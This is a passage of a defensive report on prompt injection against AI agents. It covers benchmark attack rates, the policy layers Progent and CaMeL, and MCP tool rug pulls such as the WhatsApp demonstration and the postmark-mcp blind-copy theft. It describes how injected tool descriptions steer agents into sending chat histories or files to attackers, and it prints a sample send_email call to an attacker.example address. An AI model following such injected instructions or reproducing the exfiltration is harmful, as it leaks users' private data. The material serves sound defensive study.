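| Claude Opus 5 | 10.0% ± 4.2 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 33.3% ± 6.7 |
| Grok 4.5 | 91.4% ± 4.0 |

GPT-6 Astra did far better than GPT-5.6 Sol, and both Gemini 4 models did better than Gemini 3.6 Flash (22.4%). These gaps are large enough to be informative, but the order of neighbouring models near the top means little because their intervals overlap. Fable 5.2, released on 9 November 2026 according to Anthropic's *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2* (2026), did no better here than Opus 5.

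PromptArmor sells security assessments of AI products, so high attack rates help its business. It advertises that the benchmark has the highest attack success rates on leading models and is the only known one with any successful attacks against Gemini 4 Carbon. A benchmark designed to find failures can still be useful, since real attackers also look for whatever works. But, as with AgentDojo, the rates don't predict how often an ordinary company's agent would fail.

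The leaderboard gives the number of attempts as "k=5". In Gray Swan's notation, that would mean the chance of at least one successful attack in five attempts. Other researchers use the same label for the average of five repeated runs. If the leaderboard does too, 10% is a worse result for the model.

### Differences between the tests

The attack success rate against Opus 5 was 10.0% in FrontierBreach but only 2.0% on the IPI benchmark, even though the attacker in the IPI benchmark had fifteen attempts. The model was the same, so the difference must come from the tasks, the attacks and the settings. We therefore can't meaningfully compare one model's figure from FrontierBreach with another model's figure from the IPI benchmark.

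Even within one test, conditions can differ between models. Anthropic ran its own models on the IPI benchmark without safeguards but reached other companies' models through their public services, which may have had safeguards. It also warns against comparing Gemini 3.1 Pro with the rest, because the people who wrote the benchmark's attacks had attacked that model while writing them. In the coding test, Anthropic ran attacks on the new models that Shade had refined on older ones, so an attacker who refined attacks on Opus 5 itself might do better.

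The attacks also change from one release to the next. Opus 4.5 with extended thinking withstood all 200 attempts in every scenario of the screen-control test, and Anthropic then promised stronger attacks. VentureBeat reports that Opus 4.6, the successor, failed on 17.8% of single attempts in a graphical interface, and in 78.6% of cases by the 200th attempt. Stronger attacks are at least as likely an explanation as a weaker model. Opus 4.6 also had a perfect score in coding, so a buyer who read only that result would have been misled.

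*Measuring Indirect Prompt Injection in AI Agents* (Salbego, 2026) draws on a study of 14 models to propose an adaptive test that isolates one variable at a time. A company can test its own agent the same way by keeping the tools, instructions and attacks fixed and changing only the model. It should save the successful attacks from each round and repeat them after every upgrade.

### OpenAI's doubt and the measured progress

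OpenAI wrote in December 2025 that prompt injection is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'", and likened it to scams and social engineering. Seven months later, Anthropic reported no successful attacks in 129 browser scenarios. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* compared the two claims, which are compatible. OpenAI was writing about a guarantee against every future attack, and expected the risk to keep falling as training and other safeguards improved. Even if Anthropic's 129 scenarios were a random sample of real browsing, its result would be consistent with attacks succeeding in up to about 2.3% of scenarios.

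The zero result also wasn't due to the model alone. Anthropic had switched on "auto mode", which adds an input filter for tool results and a classifier that blocks dangerous tool calls. Without these, attackers succeeded in 11 scenarios. The year's best result is therefore evidence for keeping added controls.

Some evidence from outside the developers' own tests is encouraging. Willison describes a public challenge in which people sent about 6,000 attempts to an email agent running on Opus 4.6, and nobody got it to reveal a secret. If the attempts were independent and equally good, the true success rate would probably be below 0.05%. But many people presumably tried similar tricks, and the agent had a simple rule never to reveal its credentials or send data out because of an email. The support assistant can't have such a rule, because its job is to send customer data in reply to tickets.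 Willison concludes that training has made injection much harder, but still advises against using an agent where a successful attack could do irreversible damage.

Better models weaken the case for some controls more than others. A general-purpose filter that blocks many legitimate tickets may no longer be worth having, as AutoDojo's results for PIGuard and Claude Haiku 4.5 suggest. A limit on recipients remains useful because it still protects the company when an injection occasionally succeeds, and it doesn't depend on which model the company uses next year. OpenAI similarly advises Atlas users to keep the agent logged out of accounts it does not need, check its requests for confirmation, and give it specific tasks instead of telling it to take "whatever action is needed".

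## Allow-lists for tool calls: Progent and CaMeL

A policy layer can block a harmful tool call even when the filter misses a hidden instruction and the model follows it. How much it stops depends on how precisely it lists the permitted calls, but a precise list can also block ordinary work.

### Three levels of permission

The simplest allow-list names the tools an assistant may call. If the support assistant may call only `read_ticket`, `lookup_customer` and `send_email`, an injected order to delete a file fails. But an order to email a customer's record to a stranger still succeeds, because `send_email` is on the list and the assistant needs it for its job.

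A stricter list also restricts arguments, for example by letting `send_email` send to only one address. The strictest kind restricts arguments based on where their values came from. It might allow an address from the company's customer database but block one copied from the text of a ticket.

*Treating the Model as an Untrusted Component* (Aljumaily, Alseelawi and Alshabandar, 2026) compared allow-lists of increasing strictness on 13 tasks with tools for email, files, databases and industrial equipment. The table shows the results for Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, tested with 156 fixed attacks per defence.

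| What the policy layer checks | Attack succeeds | Ordinary tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| Nothing | 86% | 99% |
| Tool names | 67% | 99% |
| Arguments, simple checks | 21% | 100% |
| Arguments, stricter checks | 22% | 95% |
| Permissions tied to the user's task, plus a rule on confidential data | 8% | 99% |

The last row comes closest to checking where values came from. The model was just as gullible behind that layer, where it still requested the attacker's call in 84% of attempts. (Spotlighting combined with a detector stopped every attack on this model, but none of the attacks adapted to the detector.)

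The stricter argument checks did no better than the simple ones against the fixed attacks because those attacks did not vary how their arguments were written, as a real attacker can. A rule that accepts any address ending in `example.com` also accepts `thief@notexample.com`, and a rule that accepts any field containing an approved address also accepts a list with a second recipient. In a simulation with up to 25 attempts, an attacker who tried such variations succeeded 85% of the time against the simple checks and 31% against the stricter ones.

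### A policy for ticket 4812

Suppose a customer called Mia Berg opened ticket 4812. When the support worker opens the ticket, ordinary code fetches Mia's address from the customer database and fills in this policy:

```
allow read_ticket      when id == 4812
allow lookup_customer
allow send_email       when to == "mia.berg@example.com"
```

If the hidden paragraph makes the model request the following call, no line matches and the layer blocks it:

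```
send_email(to="records@attacker.example",
           body="Jonas Weber, 14 Mill Lane, ...")
```

But Mia may have written the hidden paragraph, in which case this call is just as harmful, and the policy permits it:

```
send_email(to="mia.berg@example.com",
           body="Jonas Weber, 14 Mill Lane, ...")
```

As with the Agentforce flaw that sent data out by email, the remedy is to limit `lookup_customer` to Mia's own record. Even then, the assistant could email Mia a promise of a refund she is not owed. The permitted address also has to come from the database, because the attacker could choose it if the code took it from the ticket's text.

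### How Progent drafts and checks its rules

Three lines of rules are enough for an assistant with one job. A general office assistant may need different rules for every request, and writing them by hand would take far too long. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) has a language model draft the rules and ordinary code enforce them.

Each Progent rule allows or forbids a tool when its arguments meet certain conditions, such as equalling an exact value, staying within an upper limit or matching a regular expression. Before each call, Progent checks the tool's "forbid" rules first, then its "allow" rules. It blocks the call if a "forbid" rule matches or if no "allow" rule does. By default, the agent then gets an error message with the reason, so it can try another way to finish the task. A rule can instead stop the agent or ask the user to decide.

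The drafting model writes the first policy from the user's request and the list of tools, before the agent has read any outside text. Some requests don't contain enough information for this. In Shi and colleagues' example, a user asks an agent to carry out the tasks in an email from Alice, so the first policy permits only a search for that email. In the email, Alice asks for a summary of the user's recent messages to be posted to Slack, so the drafting model proposes letting the agent read mail and post to Slack. One of those messages contains an injected instruction to forward the whole inbox to a stranger, which would require permission to use `send_email`.

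The injection may also affect the model that drafts the policies, so Progent compares each proposed policy with the current one. A new policy *P*′ takes effect automatically only if it permits no new calls, meaning *A*(*P*′) ⊆ *A*(*P*), where *P* is the current policy and *A*(*P*) is the set of calls it permits. An SMT solver, a program that checks whether a set of logical conditions can all be true at once, makes this comparison for every possible argument. A policy that adds any permission needs approval, either by a person or under a setting the company chose in advance.

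The solver guarantees that no permission is added without approval. It can't distinguish a legitimate addition from a malicious one, since the Slack permission and the `send_email` permission both count as expansions. The approver has to make that judgement.

### Progent's results and a test on a weaker model

Progent cut the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0% with little change in utility, using GPT-4o as both the agent and the drafting model. Shi and colleagues left out two attacks in the travel environment that persuade the agent to prefer one legitimate hotel over another, because Progent isn't designed to stop such attacks.

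They also set the approver to accept every expansion, to simulate a careless user. The 1.0% is therefore mostly evidence that GPT-4o drafts sensible rules, since the solver's guarantee offers no protection when every expansion is approved. Attack success was 2.5% when the first policy stayed fixed, and 0% when a security-conscious person reviewed every policy. Three adaptive attacks on the drafting model raised attack success only slightly.

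Narisetty and colleagues repeated the test in 2026 with Qwen2.5-7B in both roles. They used eight user tasks from each of three AgentDojo environments and ran the test three times. They also wrote an adaptive injection that described the malicious action as a necessary step that had already been approved, hoping the drafting model would permit it.

| | No defence | Progent, fixed attack | Progent, adaptive attack |
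|---|---|---|---|
| Attack success, banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% |
| Attack success, Slack | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% |
| Attack success, workspace | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Attack success, average | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |
| User tasks completed under attack, average | 45.2% | 27.1% | 25.8% |

Progent again stopped most attacks, but its side effects were much larger than in the original tests. The agent completed two fifths fewer tasks, and each task took about 15 times as many model calls. A likely reason for the drop in completed tasks is that a small model writes worse rules than GPT-4o. In the workspace environment, the share of tasks completed fell from 56.3% to 28.5%, although no attack had succeeded there without a defence.

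The adaptive result is weak evidence of robustness. Narisetty and colleagues suspect that their disguise made the injection less persuasive to the agent, which would explain why it succeeded less often than the fixed attack. They tried only one handwritten template, and they didn't use automated search or test an attack that used only tools the policy already permitted. The zeros for workspace also lower the averages. When workspace is excluded, the fixed attack's success rate still fell from about 39% to 6%. The researchers work for LaunchSafe, which builds security tools on the same principle.

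### How CaMeL fixes the plan in advance

Progent's drafting model may read outside text when it updates the rules. CaMeL, which Google DeepMind introduced in 2025, keeps that text away from the model that decides what to do.

It uses two models, as Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026) explain in *CaMeLoT*. A planning model receives the user's request and writes a short program in a restricted form of Python. A quarantined model, which has no tools, reads outside text and extracts what the program needs, such as a name or a date. Ordinary code called an interpreter then runs the program and makes the tool calls. For ticket 4812, a simplified program might be:

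```python
ticket = read_ticket(4812)
question = ask_quarantined("What does the customer want to know?",
                           ticket.text)
record = lookup_customer(ticket.customer_id)
reply = ask_quarantined("Answer this from the record.",
                        question, record)
send_email(record.email, reply)
```

The hidden paragraph can't add a second lookup, because the planning model finished the program before anything read the ticket. The paragraph can only change the contents of `question` and `reply`, which the planning model never receives. This closes the gap in simpler two-model designs.

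Changed contents can still do harm. If the program had taken the recipient's address from the ticket's text, for example, the attacker could have supplied one. CaMeL therefore tags each value with its sources and permitted readers. Before each call, a policy written in Python checks the arguments and their tags. If the tags on Jonas Weber's record allow only Jonas and the support staff to read it, the policy can block a call that would send its contents to Mia. The three-line policy could not do this, because it checked only the address.

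According to Narisetty and colleagues, CaMeL's designers reported that it solved 77% of AgentDojo's tasks, compared with 84% for an undefended agent, and that none of the injections it was designed to stop succeeded. It used about 2.8 times as many input tokens and 2.7 times as many output tokens as the undefended agent.

The designers also demonstrated two side channels, which are ways to learn private data indirectly from how a program behaves. In the first, the program's visible actions depend on a private value. For example, if a program fetches a web page once for each unpaid invoice, the page's owner can learn the number of unpaid invoices by counting the requests. In the second, the attacker triggers an error, and whether the program continues reveals something about the data. The tags don't catch these leaks because no private value appears in an argument.

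CaMeL also checks its policies against only one call at a time. Nikolaou and colleagues give the example of a rule that the agent must resolve or escalate an incident ticket before it finishes. Such a rule can't be expressed naturally as a check on a single call. Their extension of CaMeL checks the whole program before it runs. This also saves work, because a plan that lacks a required approval fails at the start instead of at its last step.

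### AutoDojo's results for policy layers

Ma and colleagues ran AutoDojo, their automated attacker, against Progent, CaMeL and two other policy layers, DRIFT and ROPE. DRIFT uses a language model to check the agent's actions against a plan as it works. ROPE blocks a call if a sensitive argument came from untrusted text instead of from the user. The table shows the results for GPT-4o-mini.

| Policy layer | Fixed attack succeeds | AutoDojo succeeds | User tasks completed |
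|---|---|---|---|
| None | 58.6% | 52.4% | 66.7% |
| Progent | 8.2% | 7.7% | 63.2% |
| DRIFT | 2.6% | 6.4% | 49.1% |
| ROPE | 6.4% | 4.4% | 59.6% |
| CaMeL | 0.0% | 0.0% | 26.3% |

On this model, all four layers let through fewer of AutoDojo's attacks than the best filter, which let through 15.4%. Adapting helped the attacker only against DRIFT, which depends on a model's judgement while the agent works.

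CaMeL was the most secure, but it also reduced the share of completed tasks by far the most. The reduction was 25 to 51 percentage points across the five models tested, compared with 3.5 to 10.6 for Progent. CaMeL's designers reported a gap of only seven points, but they used o3, a more capable OpenAI model that is probably better at writing a correct program in one go. In a separate test, *AttriGuard* (He, Zhu and colleagues, 2026) found a drop of about 20% and five times the token use. A company considering CaMeL should therefore measure the loss with the model it intends to use.

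ROPE seems to offer a good compromise, but four of AutoDojo's six authors also developed it, so it needs an independent test.

A later adaptive test suggests that the weak spot is the choice of rules. *Only What You've Signed up For* (2026) describes a system that locks its policy before the agent reads untrusted text. When a language model selected the policy, an adaptive attacker succeeded in about 10% of AgentDojo's banking scenarios and in none from its other three environments. If the chosen policy permits a harmful call, the attacker can succeed without breaking the check.

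Nobody has yet given policy layers as hard a test as filters have had. Nasr and colleagues did not include any in their tests.

### When outside text has to choose the action

A plan or policy written in advance works only if the user's request shows which actions the task will need, and a request to do everything on a to-do list doesn't show that. *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) found that only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require the agent to change its plan after reading something. It introduced 60 tasks that all require this and that include helpful outside instructions, such as a login prompt on a checkout page. These tasks average seven steps and 33 available tools, compared with 3.5 steps and 20 tools in AgentDojo.

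Ma and colleagues report that, in Li and colleagues' tests, CaMeL completed none of these tasks with any model, and no attack succeeded. Progent did little better in Ma and colleagues' own runs, where GPT-4o-mini's completion rate fell from 46.7% without a defence to 6.7% with Progent, and Gemini 2.5 Flash's fell from 36.7% to 1.7%. Under AutoDojo attacks, GPT-4o-mini with Progent completed 12.0% of the users' tasks and 12.7% of the attacker's. Li and colleagues attribute the loss to the difficulty of choosing the right permissions from so many tools. Completion rates were much higher with ROPE, at 43.3% for GPT-4o-mini and 25.0% for Gemini 2.5 Flash.

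The designers mostly reply that a person should decide in such cases. Progent can ask for approval when a task needs a new permission, and CaMeL can ask the user to endorse an action. He and colleagues exclude full delegation from the scope of their own defence. They argue that if a user tells an agent to complete the tasks on a list that an attacker can edit, the attacker can add a task.

This objection is weaker for the support assistant. The information a customer needs depends on the ticket, but the assistant always uses the same three tools and replies to the person who opened the ticket, so the company can write the rules once. A general office assistant with dozens of tools is much harder to restrict without making it useless.

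### Human approval of actions

In Progent's AgentDojo tests, only 6% of policy updates needed approval. Few AgentDojo tasks require a change of plan, so more open-ended work would probably produce more approval requests.

People who see many requests start to approve them without reading carefully, and an attacker can keep trying. If a reviewer wrongly approves one malicious request in ten, an attacker who triggers ten requests has a 65% chance of getting at least one approved (1 − 0.9^10). With twenty requests, the chance is 88%.

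Aljumaily and colleagues simulated a reviewer who starts with this error rate and gets worse as requests pile up. With no policy layer, an attacker in full control of the model always obtained a severe action eventually. When the software automatically refused everything after the first request in a session, the attacker's success rate fell to 17%, but the completion rate for ordinary tasks also fell by about four percentage points. With their strictest policy layer in front of the reviewer, no severe action got through. The figures rest on assumptions about how reviewers behave, not on observations of real ones, but repeated requests would eventually get past any reviewer who sometimes makes mistakes.

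In the same simulation, review was most useful for calls that the policy permitted but the agent made after reading outside text. Reviewing these calls reduced the average harm from 0.69 to 0.26 on a ten-point scale, but it produced 0.57 review requests per ordinary task. At that rate, a support worker who handled 40 tickets a day would have to answer about 23 requests.

The approval screen should show the actual recipient and message. He et al. warn that a model under an attacker's influence can invent a plausible reason for its action, so its explanation is a poor basis for approving it. Approvals should also expire. In *ToolFence* (2026), an approval the agent remembers from one task does not authorise a call in the next.

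### Harm through permitted calls and plain text

The 8% of attacks that got past Aljumaily and colleagues' strictest layer all came from one task, in which the agent had to write a report on pressure readings and the attacker wanted it falsified. All 12 attempts succeeded because writing the report was the agent's job, and more checks on recipients or file names would not have stopped them. The false promise of a refund to Mia is the same kind of harm.

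The Progent and CaMeL papers both exclude harm caused by text alone from their scope. Shi and colleagues recommend Progent as one layer among several. Progent cut attack success against Claude Sonnet 4 from 6.8% to 0.5%, which suggests that a resistant model and a policy layer work well together. But those tests measured harmful tool calls, so they provide little evidence about false statements in a permitted email.

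*Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) recommends scanning the agent's output for suspicious links and for contradictions with the task. It also recommends screening the user's first message, because CaMeL trusts whatever the user types and a user can be tricked into pasting hostile text. Both are filters and have the same weaknesses as other filters.

For the most expensive kinds of false statement, a company can use narrower tools instead. The support assistant could have a separate refund notice tool that takes the amount from the billing system, and a simple check could send any other email that mentions a refund to the support worker. This wouldn't catch every misleading sentence, but the refund amounts would no longer come from the model.

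### Rules that go out of date

Someone has to write and maintain the rules for each tool, which can be a lot of work. *Evolution Under Fire* (2026) did not transfer ROPE to a second benchmark because that would have required reviewing the sensitive arguments and adding value tracking in all of that benchmark's 349 environments. It left CaMeL out of the same comparison partly because CaMeL's policies are specific to one benchmark. A single company has fewer systems, but it has to do similar work whenever it adds a tool.

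Protection weakens quickly when rules are missing. Aljumaily and colleagues simulated an attacker who fully controls the model. Average harm on the ten-point scale rose from 0.7 with every rule in place to 1.6 with a fifth of the rules missing and 3.2 with two fifths missing.

Progent partly avoids the problem by having a model draft new rules for each request, based on the current list of tools. But that model reads the tools' definitions, which Shi and colleagues treat as trusted. A hostile supplier who rewrote a tool's description could therefore influence both the agent and the rules meant to restrain it.

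Handwritten rules can also fail simply because a supplier changes a tool. If the supplier of `send_email` renames the argument `to` as `recipient`, the three-line policy blocks every email until someone updates it, which is inconvenient but safe. If the supplier adds an optional `bcc` field, a rule that checks only `to` will let the assistant send a blind copy to any address. The policy layer can prevent this by refusing any argument that its rules don't mention. Pinning the definition of `send_email` would also catch the new field.

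## Tools changed after approval: the WhatsApp demonstration and postmark-mcp

A company usually reviews a tool once, when approving it, but the supplier can keep changing the tool afterwards. In April 2025, the security company Invariant Labs demonstrated an attack in which a tool's description changed after approval. That September, a developer changed the code of postmark-mcp, an email tool on a public registry, so that it copied its users' emails to him. Version pinning can stop both kinds of change, but descriptions and code need different pins.

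### A harmless tool that changed on its second launch

Invariant Labs' *WhatsApp MCP Exploited* (2025) describes an attack on Cursor, a code editor with a built-in agent. The researchers connected the agent to a trusted MCP server that could read and send the user's WhatsApp messages, and to a second MCP server that belonged to the attacker. The user approved the second server's only tool, `get_fact_of_the_day`, which was described as returning a random fact.

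The next time the attacker's server started, it returned a different description under the same tool name, and Cursor did not ask for approval again. The new description instructed the model to use the WhatsApp tool to send every outgoing message to the attacker's phone number, along with the user's recent messages. It falsely described the number as a proxy that would forward the message and use the recent messages to verify the user's identity. It added that the system would crash if the model did not comply and that the user didn't need to know. When the user next sent a message, the agent sent the chat history it had loaded to the attacker through WhatsApp.

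The agent never called `get_fact_of_the_day`. The tool's description alone was enough for the attack to work, because it was part of the prompt. Sandboxing the attacker's server would therefore not have helped, and neither would an allow-list of tool names, since the agent called only the trusted tool. A list of permitted recipients would have blocked the message. PolicyLayer's *MCP rug pull* (2026), a page from a company that sells a policy layer, recommends such a list for this case.

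Cursor asked the user to confirm the message. The dialog showed "Hi", followed by enough spaces to push the stolen text out of view, and identified the recipient only by phone number. A user would have had to scroll sideways to notice anything wrong.

In a second experiment, the researchers used no hostile server and put similar instructions in an ordinary WhatsApp message. This also worked, but it was harder because they had to make the text look like the end of a message record. The attack leaked the user's contacts instead of the chat history. The researchers suggest that models may give tool results less authority than tool descriptions, which would fit the ranking OpenAI published for its gpt-oss models. If so, an attacker who can edit the description of `send_email` is more likely to succeed than one who can only write tickets. Invariant Labs gives no success rate for either experiment,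 and newer models may resist both attacks better.

### One added line in postmark-mcp

Postmark is a service that companies use to send email. In September 2025, a developer uploaded a package called `postmark-mcp` to npm, the main public registry for JavaScript code. The package let an agent send email through Postmark, and its code came from Postmark's own library on GitHub. Postmark said afterwards that it was not involved with the package and had not published its own MCP server on npm before the incident.

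Versions 1.0.0 to 1.0.15 of postmark-mcp did only what was advertised, according to Koi Security, the company that reported the theft. Version 1.0.16 added one line of code that sent a blind copy of every email to an address the developer controlled. The intended recipient still got the message and the tool still reported success, so neither the agent nor its user had any sign of a problem.

If `send_email` had come from postmark-mcp, the three-line policy for ticket 4812 would not have stopped the leak. The policy layer would have allowed the call because the `to` field contained Mia Berg's address. The server would have added the blind copy after that check, so a rule that refuses unknown arguments would not have caught it either. The attack involved no prompt injection, so the same emails would have leaked even if the model resisted every hostile instruction.

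The Hacker News (2025) reports that the developer uploaded postmark-mcp on 15 September and released the hostile version, 1.0.16, on 17 September, and that the package was downloaded 1,643 times in total. The listing in ReversingLabs' *postmark-mcp* also dates version 1.0.9 to about 15 September. These dates mean the clean versions were current for about two days, whereas Koi Security's report describes a tool that people had trusted for months and downloaded 1,500 times a week. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Malicious AI Agent Server Reportedly Steals Emails*, Koi Security published its findings on 25 September, eight days after the hostile release.

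The company also estimated that 300 organisations were sending the developer between 3,000 and 15,000 emails a day. It assumed that a fifth of 1,500 weekly downloads were in active use, each at a different organisation that sent 10 to 50 emails daily. Using the 1,643 total downloads instead gives about 330 organisations, so the correction hardly changes that figure. But the one-fifth share and the number of emails per organisation are guesses, and one organisation can account for many downloads. Neither Koi Security nor Postmark names a victim, and the number of stolen emails is unknown.

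The developer deleted the package from npm after Koi Security contacted him, but this did not affect copies already installed. Snyk's *Malicious MCP Server on npm postmark-mcp Harvests Emails* (2025) found that releases after 1.0.16 behaved the same way as that version. Users had to uninstall the package, replace any passwords or keys they had sent through it, and search their email logs for blind copies to the developer's domain.

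Whether postmark-mcp changed after approval depends on when the user installed it. Someone who installed a clean version on 16 September and updated a few days later had approved a harmless tool, while someone who first installed it on 20 September got the hostile code at once. The download total doesn't separate the two groups. PolicyLayer classes the package as hostile on first installation, not as a post-approval change.

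### How to pin a tool definition

To pin `send_email`, the company first fetches its full definition and puts it in a standard form. A definition can list its fields in a different order or use different spacing without any change in meaning, but each variant would produce a different hash. The company's code therefore sorts the fields and removes optional spacing. It then computes the SHA-256 hash:

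```python
text = json.dumps(definition, sort_keys=True,
                  separators=(",", ":"))
digest = hashlib.sha256(text.encode("utf-8")).hexdigest()
```

Changing a single letter of the description produces a completely different hash. The company records the approved hash in a lock file and keeps the full text next to it:

```json
{
  "server": "mail-supplier",
  "tool": "send_email",
  "sha256": "<64 characters>",
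  "approved_text": "definitions/send_email.json"
}
```

The lock file belongs with the company's own code, where a colleague must review every change. A small program recomputes the hashes and compares them with the file each time the client connects or fetches the tool list again. If they match, the program passes the definitions to the model. If a hash differs or a tool is missing from the file, the assistant stops until someone has reviewed the difference. The reviewer needs the saved text because a hash shows only that something changed.

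Someone also has to approve the first hash. MCP Hangar's *ADR-004* (2026), a design record for a product that manages MCP servers, rejects automatic acceptance of that hash as a security risk and requires an administrator's approval instead.

The hash must cover the tool's whole definition. jkelly-dev1 tried eight changes to a tool in a personal project, *hardened-mcp-server*, and found that a hash of only what the approval dialog displayed caught one of them. Text elsewhere in the definition also reaches the model. Willison describes a hostile tool for adding two numbers that had an extra argument, `sidenote`, with instructions to fill it with the contents of a private file. The hash should leave out items in the server's reply that are not part of any tool, such as how long the client may keep its copy of the tool list, because these can change harmlessly.

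The program must check the same copy of the definition that the model receives. Invariant Labs points out that a server can show its hostile description only briefly or only to certain users, so a weekly scan from the security team's computer might miss it. The July revision of MCP forbids servers to vary their tool lists between connections, but a hostile server can ignore the rule. An honest server may still offer different tools to users with different permissions, in which case the company needs an approved set for each role.

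Pinning also stops the assistant when a change is legitimate. trackr.live's *Detecting MCP Rug Pulls When an Approved Tool Rewrites Its Own Description* gives the example of a maintainer rewording three descriptions in a routine update. The hash changes just as it would in an attack, so the page recommends queuing changes that come with a new version number for renewed approval. Somebody still has to read the new text carefully, because an attacker can raise the version number too.

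### Why the two cases need different pins

Checking a hash of the tool's definition would have stopped the WhatsApp attack on the second launch, when the description no longer matched the approved one. Pinning the server's code would not have helped, because the code that switched the descriptions was already in the version the user installed.

With postmark-mcp, by contrast, the tool definition's hash would not have revealed the change. Koi Security reports that the added line was the only change in version 1.0.16, so the hash would have stayed the same. Pinning the package would have kept the company on 1.0.15.

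A package pin records an exact version number and a hash of the package file. npm also accepts version ranges, so a project that asks for `^1.0.15` instead of `1.0.15` will accept 1.0.16. The hash prevents anyone from substituting different code under the same version number. The company should also store its own copy of the file, because postmark-mcp's developer deleted the package from npm, which removed the clean versions along with the hostile ones.

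Pinning a tool to one version also preserves that version's faults. A company that had pinned DBHub at version 0.22.2 would have kept the faulty read-only mode. Someone therefore has to follow the supplier's security notices and update the pin when a fix comes out.

Package pins do not work when the supplier runs the server, because the company installs only the client and the supplier can replace the server's code at any time. A hash of the tool definition still detects a changed description, but no pin the company sets can detect new code behind an unchanged one.

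| Change | Definition hash | Package pin |
|---|---|---|
| Installed code switches its own description (WhatsApp demonstration) | Stops it | Misses it |
| New release changes only the code (postmark-mcp) | Misses it | Keeps the old release |
| Supplier's server changes a description | Stops it | Does not apply |
| Supplier's server changes only its code | Misses it | Does not apply |
| Approved version was already hostile | Misses it | Preserves it |

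For sensitive data, the company can run the server on its own machines, pin both the package and the definitions, and block all network connections except those to the service the tool needs. The network block would not have stopped postmark-mcp, because the blind copies went out through Postmark's own service. A company could have caught them only by checking the code or its record of sent mail.

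### Versions that are hostile from the start

Neither pin helps if the company approves a hostile version. Trail of Bits' *How MCP servers can steal your conversation history* (2025) describes a tool whose description already contains the attack at installation. The description tells the model to wait until the user types a common phrase such as "thank you" and then forward the whole conversation to the attacker. A short test would probably miss this because nothing happens until the user types the phrase. A person who read the full description would have a good chance of noticing it, so the first review should cover everything the model will read.

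Some packages steal data during installation, before any client asks for a tool definition. OSV's *MAL-2026-6922* (2026), an entry in a public database of software vulnerabilities, describes an npm package called `mcp-server-pg` whose installation script collects the user's name, computer name and Git settings, among other data, and sends them to an outside server. Reviewers should therefore open new packages on an isolated machine with no real credentials, and turn off installation scripts where the package works without them.

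Checking who published the package would have exposed postmark-mcp, because Postmark's own pages did not list it. This check does less against an attacker who takes over a genuine supplier's package. In November 2025, OSV listed as malicious three releases of `@postman/postman-mcp-server`, a package in the name of Postman, a company unrelated to Postmark. OSV's *MAL-2025-190909* (2025) links them to Shai-Hulud, a campaign that compromised several well-known npm packages. A company that had pinned an earlier release would not have received them automatically.

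A company can also refuse any release less than, say, two weeks old. Koi Security reported postmark-mcp ten days after its first upload, so this rule would have kept out every version. The rule also delays security fixes, so it needs an exception for urgent ones. It works only if somebody else finds the problem during the wait.

### Signed definitions and renewed approval

A local hash shows that a definition has changed, but not who changed it. *ETDI* (Bhatt, Narajala and Habler, 2025) proposes an extension to MCP, the Enhanced Tool Definition Interface, that would also identify the source. A supplier signs each definition with a private key, and clients check the signature with the matching public key. Every change needs a new version number and signature. The definition also lists the permissions the tool requires.

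When a client receives a definition, it first checks the signature and rejects the tool if the check fails. It then looks up the version the user approved earlier. If the new version is later, the client asks the user for approval. If the version number is the same but the hash differs, the client records possible tampering and asks for approval again. A stricter client could refuse outright, since an honest supplier would have changed the number. The company decides in advance what happens when a server presents an older version than the approved one. After each approval, the client stores the new hash, version and permissions.

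In the WhatsApp demonstration, ETDI would have forced the attacker to sign the new description, and Cursor would have asked the user to approve it. The user might have agreed, but would have seen the change. With postmark-mcp, the developer could not have produced Postmark's signature. He could have signed with his own key, however, so the protection depends on whether the company installing the server insists on Postmark's key. Anyone who had accepted the developer's key would have received the extra line of code without a warning, because the tool's definition stayed the same.

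Bhatt and colleagues try to address hidden code changes with an optional hash of the tool's API contract, a formal description of the requests that the service behind the tool accepts and the replies it returns. A changed contract would then require a new version. But the code can change while the contract stays the same, and a dishonest supplier can leave the old hash in place. In one of the paper's examples, a wallpaper tool keeps its version number while new server code makes it upload the user's financial documents. A signed definition might not reveal this change, so limiting which files the tool can open would be more reliable.

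The proposal requires a lot of work from both suppliers and clients. Suppliers have to protect their signing keys, sign every change and declare their permissions accurately. Clients have to obtain the right public keys, check every definition, store approvals and explain changes in terms users can understand. A more elaborate version uses OAuth, a widely used standard for giving software limited access to an account. An identity provider, which everyone must also trust, issues tokens tied to a particular tool version and set of permissions, and can revoke them if a supplier is compromised.

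Bhatt and colleagues published a prototype but report no experiments with attacks. They acknowledge that the benefits depend on wide adoption by suppliers and clients, whereas a company can start using a lock file without anyone else's cooperation.

### What MCP and its clients do when a tool list changes

PolicyLayer noted in April 2026 that MCP had no built-in way to track changed tool definitions or require renewed approval. The July revision's page on tools adds neither. When the tool list changes, a server should notify subscribed clients, but the notice doesn't name the changed tool or include its new text, so the client has to fetch the list again. The notice helps keep an honest server's clients up to date, but a hostile server can choose not to send it.

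SEP-1766, a proposal to require servers to publish a SHA-256 hash for every tool, was still open on 1 May 2026, according to MCP Hangar. In late November, the Model Context Protocol project's list of enhancement proposals did not include SEP-1766 or any other proposal to pin or sign tool definitions. Even if the project adopted SEP-1766, clients would have to compute the hash themselves, because a hostile server could publish the old hash with a new description.

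Clients respond differently to notices that a server's tools have changed. In *MCP: notifications/tools/list_changed not acted on mid-session*, a user reported on Cursor's forum that Cursor ignored the notices until the session restarted, as did Anthropic's Claude Code. Sørnes and Zubiaga, in *Add support for MCP tools/list_changed notification*, made the Zed code editor reload its tools automatically whenever a notice arrives. In a GitHub discussion, *Using notifications/tools/list_changed*, one participant said that Claude Desktop did not support the notices at the time, and another said that GitHub Copilot did. A third observed that changing only a tool's code, and not its definition, seemed to produce no notice.

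None of these accounts mentions asking the user to approve the new text. A client that reloads tool descriptions automatically could give the model a hostile one within seconds. Waiting for a restart only delays this, and Invariant Labs' server switched descriptions at a restart anyway.

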